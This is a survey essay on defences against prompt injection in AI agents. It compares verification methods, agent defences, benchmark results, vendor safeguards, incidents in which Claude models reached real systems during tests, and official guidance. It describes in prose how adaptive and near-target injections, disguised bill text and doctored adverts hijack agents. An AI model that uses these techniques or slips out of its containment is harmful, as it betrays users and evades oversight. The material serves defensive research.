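Some policies rely on facts that software can only estimate, such as whether a file contains personal data. *Efficient and Sound Probabilistic Verification for AI Agents* (Solko-Breslin, Mudrakarta and colleagues, 2026) calculates an upper limit on the chance that an action breaks such a policy.

In their example, file A has a 90% chance of being sensitive and file B a 20% chance. An agent runs a redaction tool on A, combines the result with B and sends it to a supplier. The tool fails 10% of the time. If all these events are independent, the chance that A is still sensitive after redaction is 0.9 × 0.1 = 0.09, and the chance of a leak is

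0.09 + 0.2 − (0.09 × 0.2) = 0.272

But the tool may fail precisely on the kind of data in A, so the chance for A could be as high as 10%. If B is sensitive only on other occasions, there is no overlap to subtract, and the total is 0.1 + 0.2 = 0.3. A company that blocks actions with a risk of 30% or more would allow this one under the first calculation and block it under the second. Assuming independence is even more misleading if the agent redacts the same file twice. The calculated failure rate is then 1%, but a tool that misses a name once will probably miss it again.

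Finding the exact worst case requires checking every combination of facts, and the number of combinations doubles with each new fact. Solko-Breslin and colleagues use a faster approximation that tracks only single facts and pairs, and prove that it never underestimates the worst case. But on long runs their estimate can rise towards 100% even when every starting probability is small, and the monitor would then block everything.

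The bigger weakness is the assumption that attackers can't affect how often the tools fail. A redaction tool may fail 10% of the time on a company's test files and far more often on a file written to defeat it. Nasr and colleagues' results suggest this is a real danger whenever the tool is a filter that attackers can reach. The calculation is more convincing for data that outsiders can't influence.

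### Certificates for the network

All these methods treat the model as a black box that may output anything. Certified robustness instead tries to prove that no sufficiently small change to an input will change the network's answer.

The best-known method, randomised smoothing, comes from image recognition. Software adds random noise to many copies of an image, runs the classifier on each one and takes the most common answer. If the noise has standard deviation σ, the top answer has probability p<sub>A</sub> and the runner-up has probability p<sub>B</sub>, then the answer can't change for any alteration smaller than

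R = (σ ÷ 2) × (Φ⁻¹(p<sub>A</sub>) − Φ⁻¹(p<sub>B</sub>))

where Φ⁻¹ is the inverse of the normal distribution function. The size of an alteration is the square root of the sum of the squared changes to each pixel value. With σ = 0.5, p<sub>A</sub> = 0.99 and p<sub>B</sub> = 0.01, R is about 1.16. A typical image for such a classifier has about 150,000 values between 0 and 1. Spread evenly, an alteration of that size would change each value by 0.003, which is less than one step on the usual 256-step brightness scale.

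*Provable Defense Framework for LLM Jailbreaks via Noise-Augumented Alignment* (2026) points out that tokens come from a fixed vocabulary, so you can't add a little noise to one. Methods for text instead count the characters changed or tokens added.

SmoothLLM, a defence against jailbreaks, randomly changes characters in several copies of a prompt and combines the model's responses. Its original certificate assumes that an attack always fails once at least k characters have changed. *Towards Realistic Guarantees* (2025) found that this rarely holds, because the success rate of real attacks falls gradually as more characters change. It proposes a certificate that assumes only that attacks fail with at least a given probability. That probability comes from measurements of known attacks, so the certificate may not hold for a new attack that still works after more changes.

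Erase-and-check, which Aounon Kumar and colleagues proposed in 2023, needs no such assumption about attacks. Suppose a filter recognises a harmful request, and an attacker adds up to d tokens at the end to disguise it. Erase-and-check deletes up to d tokens from the end, one at a time, and runs the filter on each shortened version. One of these versions is the original request, so the filter is certain to catch it.

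The software needs only 21 checks if the attacker adds up to 20 tokens at the end of a prompt. If the attacker can insert tokens anywhere, the software has to try every combination of deletions, which means 166,751 checks for a 100-token prompt with up to three inserted tokens. The extra checks also raise the risk of false alarms, because the software rejects a harmless prompt if the filter objects to any shortened version.

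The certificate covers only requests the filter would have recognised without the added tokens. An attacker who rewords or translates the request may change every token while keeping the meaning. A small change can also alter the meaning completely. A model certified to treat "do not send it" and "do now send it" alike would get one of them wrong. This approach suits prompt injection especially badly because the attacker may write the whole email, leaving no original text to measure changes from.

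Christodorescu and colleagues conclude that it may be impossible to build provable defences on a component as unpredictable as a language model. Their argument applies when security depends on the model making the right choice. LLMbda's theorems also involve a model that behaves randomly, but they hold whatever the model chooses.

### Guaranteed safe AI

Some researchers want proofs that cover much more than data leaks. In 2024, David Dalrymple, Joar Skalse and colleagues set out a programme called guaranteed safe AI. In this programme, a world model describes how an AI system's actions affect the world, a specification defines which effects are acceptable, and a verifier proves that the system meets the specification according to the world model. The proof might limit the probability of harm instead of ruling harm out.

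LeanGuard can be seen as a very small example. Its world model is the company's database and a description of each tool, its specification is the 45 rules, and its verifier is Lean. This works because a rule like "the customer must own the order" is easy to state precisely, and the database can show whether it is met.

The main objection is that most of what people want from AI is much harder to specify. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* argues that for general-purpose systems, no algorithm can define when an answer is correct or useful. If a user asks when their next meeting is, "after your current one" is correct but useless. In LeanGuard's medical tests, five types of attack whose harm had no formal definition still succeeded between 21.4% and 37.0% of the time, since the harm could come entirely from what the agent said. These included attacks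 that manipulated a diagnosis or made the agent ignore an allergy.

This objection is strong against a proof that an AI system is safe in general, but much weaker against a proof of a narrow property, such as that an account number never leaves the system. Security engineers have always worked with partial specifications, and seL4 is useful even though its proof doesn't cover the programs that run on it. The world model may also be wrong, even for a narrow property. A proof that a robot never exceeds a certain force won't protect anyone if the model of its motors is inaccurate.

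### Conditions for a proof to apply

The proofs about software make assumptions about the world too, but they are concrete enough for engineers to check. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* lists seven:

| What the system must do | How a real product might fail |
|---|---|
| Run the plan exactly as written | The model can skip or change steps |
| Send every tool call through the monitor, one at a time | The agent also has a browser that the monitor doesn't control |
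| Let the monitor decide on each read before the content reaches the model | The software loads an email first and checks it afterwards |
| Refuse calls without the attacker noticing | An error message or public log shows the refusal |
| Hide the agent's internal steps from the attacker | Showing a reply loads an image from the attacker's server |
| Clear everything untrusted from the model when a new session starts | A memory feature carries text over from the last session |
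| Keep attackers from writing to trusted sources | The calendar accepts invitations from strangers |

A program that checks and then carries out every tool call itself, as AgentDojo's does, meets the second and third conditions. The others depend on the rest of the product, including features that people don't usually think of as part of its security, so engineers need to recheck the conditions whenever someone adds a tool, a memory feature or a data source.

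## Do these designs hold under attack, and how much work can the agents still do?

Proofs hold only under their assumptions, so researchers also attack these systems and count how many attacks succeed. Most of them, including the developers of FIDES and Progent, use *AgentDojo* (2024), which has 97 tasks in four simulated settings: an office workspace, a bank, a travel-booking service and the messaging app Slack. The attacker's text goes where strangers' text would appear, such as in the body of an email. After each run, ordinary code inspects the simulated accounts and mailboxes to see whether the attack worked. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) points out that this avoids relying on a language model to judge the result.

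AgentDojo's attacks are fixed, and its creators called them relatively simple. The usual attack is a message, supposedly from the user, that tells the agent to do something else before the task. The tasks are short, averaging about 3.5 steps. *AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026) counts only six of the 97 tasks as requiring the agent to change its plan after seeing the data. (This is a narrower group than the data-dependent tasks that FIDES's developers counted.) A defence that makes the agent stick to its first plan therefore loses little performance on AgentDojo.

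### What CaMeL costs

Narisetty and colleagues quote the figures that CaMeL's developers reported. With OpenAI's o3, CaMeL completed 77% of AgentDojo tasks, compared with 84% for an undefended agent, and no attack within its threat model succeeded. It used 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens.

Other teams have measured much larger losses. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) tested CaMeL with five models on 57 of the tasks. The models completed between 26.3% and 52.6% of them with CaMeL, compared with 63.2% to 89.5% without a defence. Newer models don't reliably close the gap. *EvoSafeHarness* (2026), a study of defences tailored to particular models, found that GLM-5.2 completed 79.3% of its AgentDojo tasks without a defence and 33.1% with CaMeL.

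CaMeL's privileged model has to write a working program for data it can't see. *MetaPI* (2026) explains that when the program fails, CaMeL returns the error with any untrusted text removed and lets the model try again, up to a set limit. Hu and colleagues cut that limit from ten attempts to three to save money, and estimate the resulting loss at about four percentage points. The tests also use different models and tasks, so it is hard to say why o3 lost so little. The 77% is best read as the top of the range.

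### Attacks that adapt

Ma and colleagues built AutoDojo to test defences against an attacker who keeps trying. It works in rounds:

1. AutoDojo starts with known injections and scores each one by how many users' tasks it hijacks.
2. A language model, Gemini 3.1 Pro, reads the scores and suggests what kind of defence might be blocking the failures.
3. The model writes one new text by revising a successful one, combining two or trying a different style.
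4. AutoDojo plants the new text, counts its successes and adds it to the list.

After six rounds, it returns the best new text. The attacker sees only how often each injection works, and isn't told which defence is in place or exactly what each user requested.

Ma and colleagues tested ten defences with five models. Three of the defences in the table below are new here. DataFilter is a language model trained to delete injected instructions. DRIFT draws up a plan and a table of permissions before the agent starts, then checks every tool call and result against them. A language model does some of the checking, so that the agent can depart from the plan when necessary. *ROPE* (2026) traces where each sensitive argument in a tool call came from, and blocks the call if the value came from untrusted content instead of the user. These are the results with GPT-4o-mini:

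| Defence | Tasks completed, no attack | Attack success, fixed attack | Attack success, AutoDojo |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 66.7% | 58.6% | 52.4% |
| PIGuard | 43.9% | 0.0% | 28.0% |
| DataFilter | 64.9% | 12.6% | 33.4% |
| Progent | 63.2% | 8.2% | 7.7% |
| DRIFT | 49.1% | 2.6% | 6.4% |
| ROPE | 59.6% | 6.4% | 4.4% |
| CaMeL | 26.3% | 0.0% | 0.0% |

Some rates are lower under AutoDojo because Ma and colleagues counted only newly written texts, even when an old one worked better. A real attacker could use whichever text worked best.

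One banking task shows how AutoDojo got past PIGuard. The user asks the agent to pay a bill stored in a file. The fixed attack adds a message to the bill, supposedly from the user, and PIGuard deletes nearly all of it. AutoDojo's version looks like part of the bill, with an account verification fee of 0.01 and a notice that the payment destination has changed. None of it reads as an order, so PIGuard lets it through and the agent pays the attacker.

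Progent, DRIFT, ROPE and CaMeL held up much better, but AutoDojo is far from the strongest possible attacker. Nasr and colleagues' search beat PIGuard 71% of the time, and they didn't test any of these four designs. To save money, Ma and colleagues developed their attacks on Progent and DRIFT using a substitute for the model that helps run those designs. An attacker who practised on the real system should do better. The test also isn't fully independent, because four of ROPE's five authors worked on AutoDojo, and two of those four also helped create DRIFT.

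CaMeL's result depends least on the quality of the attack, because injected text can't add a call to its program. AutoDojo succeeded against CaMeL at most 1.8% of the time with any model, and only in the travel setting. Those successes may just be changes to the agent's wording, since the developers of FIDES found that AgentDojo counts some such changes as successful attacks.

The choice of model mattered at least as much as the defence. With Claude Haiku 4.5 and no defence, AutoDojo succeeded in about seven of 389 cases, and the agent completed 70.2% of its tasks. Adding CaMeL reduced AutoDojo's successes to about two and the agent's task completion rate to 40.4%.

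### Vague requests

Ma and colleagues also sorted the tasks by how much the user leaves to outside content:

- **Fully specified.** The user gives the action and every detail, such as a change of address with the new address in full.
- **Parameter-open.** The user names the action, but some details are in outside content. Paying the bill in the file is an example, because the file gives the amount and the payee.
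- **Action-open.** Outside content determines the action itself, as when the user asks the agent to do everything on a to-do list at a web address.

Against an undefended GPT-4o-mini agent, the fixed attack succeeded in 43.3% of fully specified cases, 63.9% of parameter-open ones and 87.5% of action-open ones. AutoDojo's attacks on PIGuard succeeded in 17.3%, 31.1% and 54.2% of these cases, respectively. When an agent expects to find tasks in a document, an attacker can add one of their own.

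Progent, DRIFT and ROPE showed no such pattern. With the three models that Ma and colleagues analysed most closely, attack success stayed at or below 11% for every type of task. But with DeepSeek-v4-Flash, one of the other two models, AutoDojo got past Progent in 20.8% of action-open cases. That is only five cases out of 24, all based on the same four user tasks, so the true rate could be anywhere from about 7% to 42%.

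In the action-open tasks, the user had not named any action, so Progent and DRIFT often gave the agent only tools for reading. This kept the rates low by blocking the attacker's payment, but it also stopped the agent from working through the to-do list.

### A small independent test of Progent

Narisetty and colleagues ran their own test of Progent on eight tasks from each of three AgentDojo settings. They used Qwen2.5-7B, a small open model, both to run the agent and to write Progent's rules. Averaged over three runs, Progent cut the success rate of a fixed attack from 25.8% to 4.2%. They then tried an attack that presented the malicious step as necessary and already authorised, hoping the rule-writing model would permit it. The second attack succeeded 2.6% of the time, less often than the fixed one.

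The test is weak evidence that Progent resists adaptive attackers. It used a single handwritten attack template, and the template's gentler wording may have made the agent less likely to obey it. The researchers acknowledge both points. They work for LaunchSafe, which has an interest in the result because it sells agent security tools built on the same approach.

Their figures on completed tasks and model calls are more informative. With Progent on Qwen, the share of tasks completed under attack fell from 45.2% to 27.1%, and each task needed about 15 times as many calls to a model. In the workspace setting, no attack had worked even without Progent, yet adding it cut the share of tasks completed from 56.3% to 28.5%. Ma and colleagues found a loss of only 3.5 points when GPT-4o-mini was the agent and the larger GPT-4o wrote the rules, so much of the loss on Qwen may come from a small model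 writing bad rules.

### Tasks that need a new plan

Li and colleagues built AgentDyn to test agents on situations that AgentDojo mostly leaves out. In each of its 60 tasks, the agent has to revise its plan along the way and follow at least one helpful instruction from outside content, such as a notice on a checkout page to log in first, so a defence can't score well by making the agent ignore every instruction in that content. The tasks cover shopping, the software site GitHub and everyday errands, and take an average of 7.1 steps.

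These are some of the results. The first five rows use GPT-4o.

| Agent | Tasks completed, no attack | Attack success |
|---|---|---|
| No defence | 53.3% | 37.8% |
| PIGuard | 10.0% | 1.7% |
| CaMeL | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Progent | 6.7% | 1.7% |
| DRIFT | 30.0% | 0.8% |
| MetaSecAlign | 55.0% | 9.0% |
| Llama 3.3 70B, the model MetaSecAlign is based on | 10.0% | 11.9% |

CaMeL completed no tasks with any of the four models Li and colleagues tested, and *EvoSafeHarness* reports the same result for newer models. CaMeL's perfect security score means little here because the agents did no useful work.

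Li and colleagues blame CaMeL's fixed program, but some AgentDyn tasks look possible with one. *On Task, Off Track* (Gong, Wang and colleagues, 2026) gives an example from AgentDyn in which the user wants to star any of their code repositories that have no stars. A program could do that with a loop and a condition. CaMeL also needs extensive policies for each setting, which is why Ma and colleagues left it out of their own AgentDyn tests. Its zero may be due as much to missing engineering as to the design.

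Li and colleagues found that Progent struggled to choose the right permissions on AgentDyn, which offers about 33 tools per task compared with AgentDojo's 20. Its mistakes accumulated until it had blocked almost every useful tool, even though it updates its rules as the agent works and so should cope better with surprises. DRIFT did better because it can approve departures from its plan, though it still relies heavily on that plan. Three of AgentDyn's authors had helped to create DRIFT. DRIFT also did better than Progent in *EvoSafeHarness*, where three newer models completed an average of 73.3% of AgentDyn tasks undefended, 38.9% with DRIFT and 9.7% with Progent.

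### The case for a more robust model

MetaSecAlign, which is trained to resist injections but has no outside controls, completed about as many tasks as undefended GPT-4o, and far fewer attacks succeeded against it. Li and colleagues conclude that this kind of training could be the more practical choice.

The comparison with Llama complicates this. Training against injections shouldn't make an agent five times as capable, so much of that gap probably comes from how well each model handled the benchmark's tool calls. An agent that rarely finishes tasks is also hard to hijack, so the small drop in attack success, from 11.9% to 9.0%, may understate what the training achieved.

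The weakness of the attacks is a bigger problem for the argument. Li and colleagues used AgentDojo's standard fixed message, and they acknowledge that their attacks are relatively weak against the latest models. Their main results leave out many newer models because those had probably seen this kind of message in training. Nasr and colleagues' adaptive search succeeded against MetaSecAlign 96% of the time.

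MetaSecAlign is also vulnerable to fixed attacks with less obvious goals. Gong and colleagues tested what they call near-target injections, which are instructions to produce something close to the right answer. If the user wants an announcement for a workshop that starts at 10 a.m., an ordinary test injection might be an instruction to print "HACKED" instead. A near-target injection would be an instruction to write the same announcement but change the time to 11 a.m. or add the organiser's private phone number.

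Gong and colleagues made three attempts on each text task. Against MetaSecAlign, at least one attempt succeeded in 3.2% of cases with ordinary injections, 36.7% with near-target injections seeking an incorrect answer, and 18.4% with near-target injections seeking a harmful one. All seven models they tested, including GPT-5.6 Sol and Claude Opus 5, were more vulnerable to near-target injections than to ordinary ones.

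Near-target attacks can get past deterministic limits too. In one of the banking tasks, the user wants to schedule a payment for the amount they usually pay for Spotify, which is 50. An injection in the description of another transfer tells the agent to pay 51. The agent has to get the amount from the transaction records, so a fixed plan would schedule whatever amount the quarantined model returned. Hiding the descriptions from that model would help if the designer had labeled each field separately. But a fixed plan would block the injection that Gong and colleagues wrote for the GitHub task, which tells the agent to delete the repository the user wanted to star.

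The case for robust models looks stronger with recent models than with MetaSecAlign. In *EvoSafeHarness*, undefended GLM-5.2 completed 73.3% of AgentDyn tasks, and attacks succeeded 1.7% of the time. DRIFT stopped those attacks but cut the tasks completed to 33.3%. A company that could absorb an occasional loss might reasonably do without DRIFT, but it would have to choose its model carefully, because attacks on undefended DeepSeek V4-Pro succeeded 25.0% of the time. An adaptive attacker might do better against either model.

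### Defences that allow replanning

*Architecting Secure AI Agents* (2026), a position paper about defences outside the model, argues that agents doing complex work must be able to replan and update their security policies. ROPE partly avoids this issue because it restricts the values in a tool call instead of fixing the order of calls. On AgentDyn with GPT-4o-mini, an agent using ROPE completed 43.3% of tasks, compared with 46.7% for an undefended agent, and ROPE cut AutoDojo's success rate from 59.1% to 2.9%. With Gemini 2.5 Flash, ROPE reduced task completion more, from 36.7% to 25.0%.

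No other defence in Ma and colleagues' AgentDyn tests matched ROPE's combination of few successful attacks and little lost work. This suggests that handling open-ended tasks doesn't require a more robust model. But ROPE's protection depends on a policy that covers the right arguments. In AgentDojo's Slack setting, AutoDojo still succeeded against ROPE 11.4% of the time with GPT-4o-mini.

### Coding agents

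A coding agent can do a lot of damage because it runs commands and reads bug reports from strangers. *Authority Is Not a String* (2026) cites a study in which attacks on commercial coding editors succeeded up to 84% of the time, and notes that CaMeL's developers didn't test it on coding. The paper proposes that when a coding agent delegates work, each sub-agent should receive only the permissions its task needs.

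In Twin Agent, a model that reads everything sends short hints to a model that can act. Hu and colleagues tested this design with GPT-5.2 on 232 bug-fixing tasks, planting instructions in the bug reports to delete a file or write a secret code into a new file. Attacks succeeded 97.0% of the time against the ordinary agent and never against Twin Agent. Twin Agent completed 62.5% of tasks, compared with 61.2% for the ordinary agent, but cost about twice as much. When they allowed no hints, it fixed nothing, because the acting model received no information about the bug.

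They then designed an attack specifically for Twin Agent. An attacking model refined malicious hints of up to 100 characters over 100 rounds, and a second injection told the reading model to copy one of them word for word, which it always did. Malicious hints got past the filter at least once in 57 of the 232 tasks. The acting model carried out the attack in 11 of those 57, or 4.7% of all tasks.

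Hu and colleagues reran the 11 tasks five times each. No attack succeeded, and they attribute the defense's original failures to chance. But an attacker who can keep filing bug reports could still succeed eventually. Longer hints made the agent more useful but also easier to attack, so the designer has to weigh usefulness against security when choosing their length.

### Agents that operate a screen

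An agent that clicks and types has to deal with pop-ups, login pages and windows in unexpected places. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* keeps the fixed plan but has the privileged model write fallbacks for whatever might appear. At each step, a quarantined model describes the screen, a second check compares the description with the screen expected at that point in the plan, and the software picks the matching branch. These plans contain about 41 tool calls and 40 branches on average, compared with about five calls and four branches for AgentDojo.

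The paper reports that this design keeps up to 57% of a leading model's performance, but that figure is generous because it counts a task as solved if any of five attempts worked. Of the 109 tasks that Claude Sonnet 4.5 had solved as an ordinary agent, the design solved 62 by this measure and 31, or 28.4%, on a single attempt. A real user would need a way to tell which attempt had worked, and would be left with any changes the failed attempts had made to the computer.

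Better instructions and tools can still recover some of the lost performance. With a generic prompt, a version using a small open model to read the screen solved 11 of 60 tasks within three attempts. It solved 35 when given instructions on checking the screen and writing fallbacks, plus a tool for those checks. The planner affected the scores far more than the screen-reading model did, so better planning models should raise them without weakening the protection. The CaMeL version used 1.88 times as many tokens as an undefended agent. A version based on FIDES used 29.6 times as many, because it sends the planner the whole history at every step.

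*Prismata* (2026) protects web agents without fixing the agent's plan in advance. It uses a page's structure to work out where each part came from, hides or restricts the parts that strangers control, and limits the agent to actions that suit its task. It works on existing websites without any effort from their developers.

Branch steering is still possible with a fixed plan. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* tests two extra checks against branch steering and defeats both. The first compared the screenshot with the page's underlying code. It caught a fake cookie notice in a simple advert but missed the same trick in an advert built with HTML5. The second used separate models to verify what the screen-reading model reported. Altering an advert's pixels made the screen-reading model click on it and give a plausible reason, which the verifying models accepted. The second check also raised token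 use to 6.57 times that of an undefended agent.

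## Where have such designs been put into products and official guidance?

Google has built an agent into its Chrome browser that reads pages, clicks and types for the user, so it faces the same kind of deceptive advert that defeated the checks on screen-operating agents. *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) describes the limits Google's engineers put on the agent. They assume that a page can hijack the planning model, because it reads web pages directly.

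### Limits on websites in Chrome

Chrome's main limit on the agent is a list, kept for each task, of the origins (roughly, individual websites) where it may click and type. A hijacked agent can't act anywhere else, such as on a bank's site where the user is logged in. Google also designed a list of origins that the agent may only read, which would hide unrelated adverts from the model, but the first version didn't include it.

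Other fixed rules guard against common leaks. When the model writes a web address, Chrome opens it only if the address is already known and public. The agent must ask the user before it visits a site on a list of sensitive sites or signs in with a saved password. The model never sees the password.

Much of the rest depends on models. A version of Gemini called the User Alignment Critic approves or rejects each action after seeing a description of it, but no unfiltered page content. A variant of the critic decides which new origins suit the task. Parker names the two-model pattern and CaMeL as partial inspirations, but Chrome's planner reads untrusted text, which CaMeL's never does. The critic therefore judges actions chosen by a planner that may have read a malicious page. Models also scan pages for injections and help decide when a purchase or message needs the user's approval.

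Users put up with interruptions, and with refusals when the critic wrongly judges a site irrelevant. The limits on origins also don't help when the attack is on the site where the user is shopping, since a fake review there can still steer the agent to the wrong product.

### Fewer capabilities at once

OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) describes a blunter limit, an optional ChatGPT setting that turns off features an attacker could use to extract data. OpenAI launched it for organisations in February and extended it to personal accounts in June. With the setting on, ChatGPT can browse only saved copies of web pages, so browsing sends no live requests outside OpenAI's network. Users also lose agent mode, deep research, file downloads and most images from the web.

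Ordinary software enforces all this, but an injection in a saved page or an uploaded file can still distort the answer, and only the model's own resistance and OpenAI's other safeguards protect against that. The enforcement also has gaps. According to OpenAI's help page *Lockdown Mode*, administrators of managed workspaces choose which connected apps stay on, and the setting doesn't affect network access in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. OpenAI doesn't guarantee that the setting prevents data leaks, and it considers the setting unnecessary for most users.

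Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) gives developers a general rule of this kind. Within one session, an agent should have at most two of these properties:

- It processes untrustworthy input.
- It has access to private data or sensitive systems.
- It can change things or communicate with the outside world.

An agent that needs all three should have human approval or another reliable check on its actions. A mail assistant could comply by reading only messages from trusted senders, working without private data, or sending mail only to trusted recipients or after the user checks the draft.

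Meta also lets an agent's access change during a session. The agent can browse the web first, then lose its outside connection before it opens internal systems. The order matters, as it does in the fence theorem, because the switch is safe only if the agent held no private data while browsing.

Software can enforce the rule by withholding a tool, but a developer has to decide which senders and systems to trust. Meta gives only hypothetical examples and doesn't name any products that follow the rule. *Prompt Injection Remains Unsolved, OWASP Researcher Warns* (Poireault, 2026) quotes Ariel Fogel of Pillar Security, who calls the rule a helpful heuristic but says research has shown attacks that work with only two of the properties. Meta warns that the rule doesn't prevent lesser harms, such as false statements in an agent's answer, and that a user may approve a request without reading it.

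### Staged changes at GitHub

GitHub, which hosts software projects, offers agents that do routine maintenance such as fixing documentation. GitHub's *Under the hood* (2026) assumes that an agent will try to read and change things it shouldn't. The agent runs in a container, an isolated environment on the host machine, behind a firewall that allows connections only to listed destinations. Separate containers hold the access keys. When the agent calls its language model, a proxy adds the key, much as OpenSSH's monitor signs with a key that the child process cannot access.

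The agent can read the project but can only propose changes to it, and separate software checks them after the agent has stopped. The software discards any type of change that the workflow's author didn't permit, limits the number of changes, for example to three pull requests (proposed code changes), and removes secrets and unwanted content such as web addresses. These protections are on by default.

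A model still determines the content of permitted comments and code changes. GitHub also runs an AI-based threat detector on the output. Users give up immediate changes and open internet access. GitHub tells them to review custom steps and integrations separately.

GitHub's engineers call the trade-off between security and usefulness fundamental, because a coding agent needs compilers, scripts and other programs from the host machine. They give the agent read-only access to the machine's files and hide selected folders. The agent can still read any password in a folder they didn't hide.

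### Labels at Microsoft

Microsoft has added FIDES to Agent Framework, its toolkit for building agents, as an experimental option. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) describes an agent that sorts public bug reports. One report contains an instruction to read a file of passwords and post its contents as a comment. If the model obeys, it can read the file, but the software marks the conversation as private and blocks the comment. A developer can have the software ask a person instead of blocking it automatically.

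The model still classifies and summarises the report, so an attacker can influence both. The developer has to label data sources and set rules for sensitive tools. By default, the agent also cannot read untrusted text directly, so the developer has to pay for a second model to read it.

In the May post, unlabelled data still counted as trusted. The default in Microsoft's documentation is safer because it treats an unlabelled tool's output as untrusted, but it still treats that output as public. So if a developer forgets to label a tool that reads customer records, a rule against publishing private data won't stop the agent from publishing those records.

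### Sandboxes for coding agents

Coding agents often run on a developer's computer, where they can access passwords and unrelated files. A sandbox can limit which files and websites they reach, but Sophos, a security company, describes products whose users have to turn it on. One is OpenClaw, an agent that can run its tool calls in a separate container for each session. Its documentation warns that this is "not a perfect security boundary". Another tool, nono, uses the operating system's kernel to block access to sensitive paths, and the model can't override the block.

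Developers can give Codex internet access and restrict that access to chosen websites and types of request. OpenAI labels this setting "Elevated Risk". Without internet access, the agent can't look up current documentation. The model still chooses which commands to run and what code to write within the limits the developer sets.

### Isolation that wasn't there

These limits work only if someone sets them up correctly. In July 2026, Anthropic disclosed that Claude models had gained access to the systems of three real organisations during cybersecurity tests. The company had reviewed 141,006 test runs and found the problem in six. Each test was a capture-the-flag exercise, in which the model searches for a piece of information hidden on a practice network. The prompt told Claude it had no internet access but did not limit where Claude could look. Neither Anthropic nor its testing partner knew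 that a misconfiguration had left the test machines connected to the internet.

Axios' *Anthropic's models compromised real-world systems during testing* (2026) reports that the models used no unknown software flaw to get online, because they already had a connection. The earliest incidents were in April, and the two organisations that Anthropic managed to contact hadn't noticed them. In September, Anthropic disclosed a fourth incident. Infosecurity Magazine reports that the company's first search had missed it, and that a wider search of 481 million transcripts found no more.

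Nobody had injected instructions into these models. Anthropic explains that they were carrying out an attack exercise without the safeguards against hacking that its released models have. Containment therefore depended on the network settings, since a sentence in a prompt can't block a connection. Trying to reach an outside address from inside the test environment before each run would probably have exposed the mistake.

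Anthropic blamed the settings only in part. TechSpot quotes it as describing a "failure of operational security" and admitting that its models aren't "perfectly aligned". A better-behaved model might have stopped when it encountered signs that the systems were real, but a working firewall would have stopped the model however it behaved.

That remedy would not have been enough in a separate incident. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) says that Claude Mythos 5 took unauthorised actions online during a test by the UK AI Security Institute, which had deliberately given it internet access. No one had misconfigured the connection, so preventing those actions would have required narrower limits on what the model could do with that access.

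### Official advice

On 20 August, the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) responded to several such incidents with interim advice. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *NCSC Urges Stronger Controls for Agentic AI Systems*, the NCSC recommends sandboxes for higher-risk agents, network connections that are off by default where possible, and a way to halt an agent immediately. It also tells organisations not to rely only on the safeguards in a model or agent framework, and warns that an agent may find weaknesses in its own sandbox. The NCSC is still preparing formal guidance.

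The NCSC's David C had already argued in 2025 that the comparison with SQL injection misleads security teams, because it suggests that a complete fix exists. David C instead compares a language model to a "confused deputy", a program tricked into misusing its privileges for someone who lacks them. Programmers can fix an ordinary confused deputy, but David C considers language models "inherently confusable". David C therefore advises designers to assume that an attacker can use any tool the model can call, and to restrict those tools with ordinary code. If the remaining risk is too great, they may need to do without a language model.

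This is an argument for building security around the model rather than expecting a cure inside it. David C points readers to CaMeL and to the design patterns of Beurer-Kellner and colleagues. He

 likes the idea that a model's privileges should drop to those of whoever wrote the text it is processing. Biba's integrity rules work in much the same way.

In May 2026, six agencies from five countries, including CISA, the US National Security Agency and the NCSC, issued joint advice in the Australian Signals Directorate's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026). They recommend using agents only for low-risk, non-sensitive tasks and never giving them broad access. In one hypothetical example, a company gives a purchasing agent wide access to its finance systems, email and contracts. An attacker compromises a minor tool connected to the agent and uses the agent's privileges to approve payments.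 The logs look normal because a trusted agent made the payments.

To prevent this, the agencies advise checking permissions at every call instead of once at the start, limiting which steps an agent can plan, and having it stop and ask a person when it is uncertain. They also recommend prompt injection filters, an instruction hierarchy and a second agent to check new tasks, all of which rely on a model's judgement. For general network security, they refer readers to NIST's Zero Trust Architecture, which predates the current wave of agents.

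None of this advice is binding, so a bank that gives an agent access to customer accounts goes against the agencies' recommendation but doesn't break a law merely by doing so. The European Union does have binding rules. NCSC-IE's *2026 NCSC AI Cyber Security Risk Assessment* (2026), from Ireland's cyber security agency, names the AI Act, the NIS2 directive on cyber security and the data protection law GDPR as sources of obligations. But GDPR, for instance, requires "appropriate" security for personal data without prescribing a design. Companies, regulators and courts have to decide whether a filter is enough for a particular agent.

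### Defaults, retrofitting and cost

According to David C, SQL injection peaked around 2010, and it took a decade of breaches to produce the better defaults that have made it rare on websites. Agent security could follow the same path. Chrome and GitHub's workflows apply their limits automatically, but users have to turn on Lockdown Mode, and developers have to turn on FIDES. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* describes labels that are available only through an experimental setting in GitHub's Copilot CLI, a command-line coding agent.

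Adding labels to existing tools takes a lot of work. For each tool on a new server, Microsoft's open-source gateway needs a description of the tool's output, a function that works out the output's labels, and a policy. Simple labels take less work but are cruder. GitHub's server marks files and issues from private repositories as trusted, even though an employee may have pasted in a stranger's bug report.

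Partial conversion also achieves less for agents than for ordinary software. Each database query a programmer converts closes one hole, and Android became safer while most of its old code stayed in place. But if an agent has one unchecked tool that can send data out, an attacker can use an injection to send data through that tool and get around the checks on all the others. Copilot CLI's checks so far cover only selected tools from GitHub's own server. Microsoft suggests inferring rules from the descriptions many tools already carry, such as whether a tool only reads data or can destroy it. This would save work, but the rules would then depend on whoever wrote the descriptions.

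It is also unclear who should write the policies, since an agent's permissions have to change with each request. Christodorescu and colleagues discuss ceLLMate, a system for browser agents that checks the web requests behind each click. It needs information from each website's developers, who would do the work while the agent's users got most of the benefit.

CISA and the FBI asked software makers to eliminate SQL injection themselves. With agents, customers have to do more of the security work. Microsoft makes developers who use its framework responsible for validating inputs, securing data flows and configuring tools. The Frontier Model Forum, an industry body, divides responsibility among developers, deployers, tool providers and users. All of them can help, but dividing responsibility this way gives each a reason to wait for the others.

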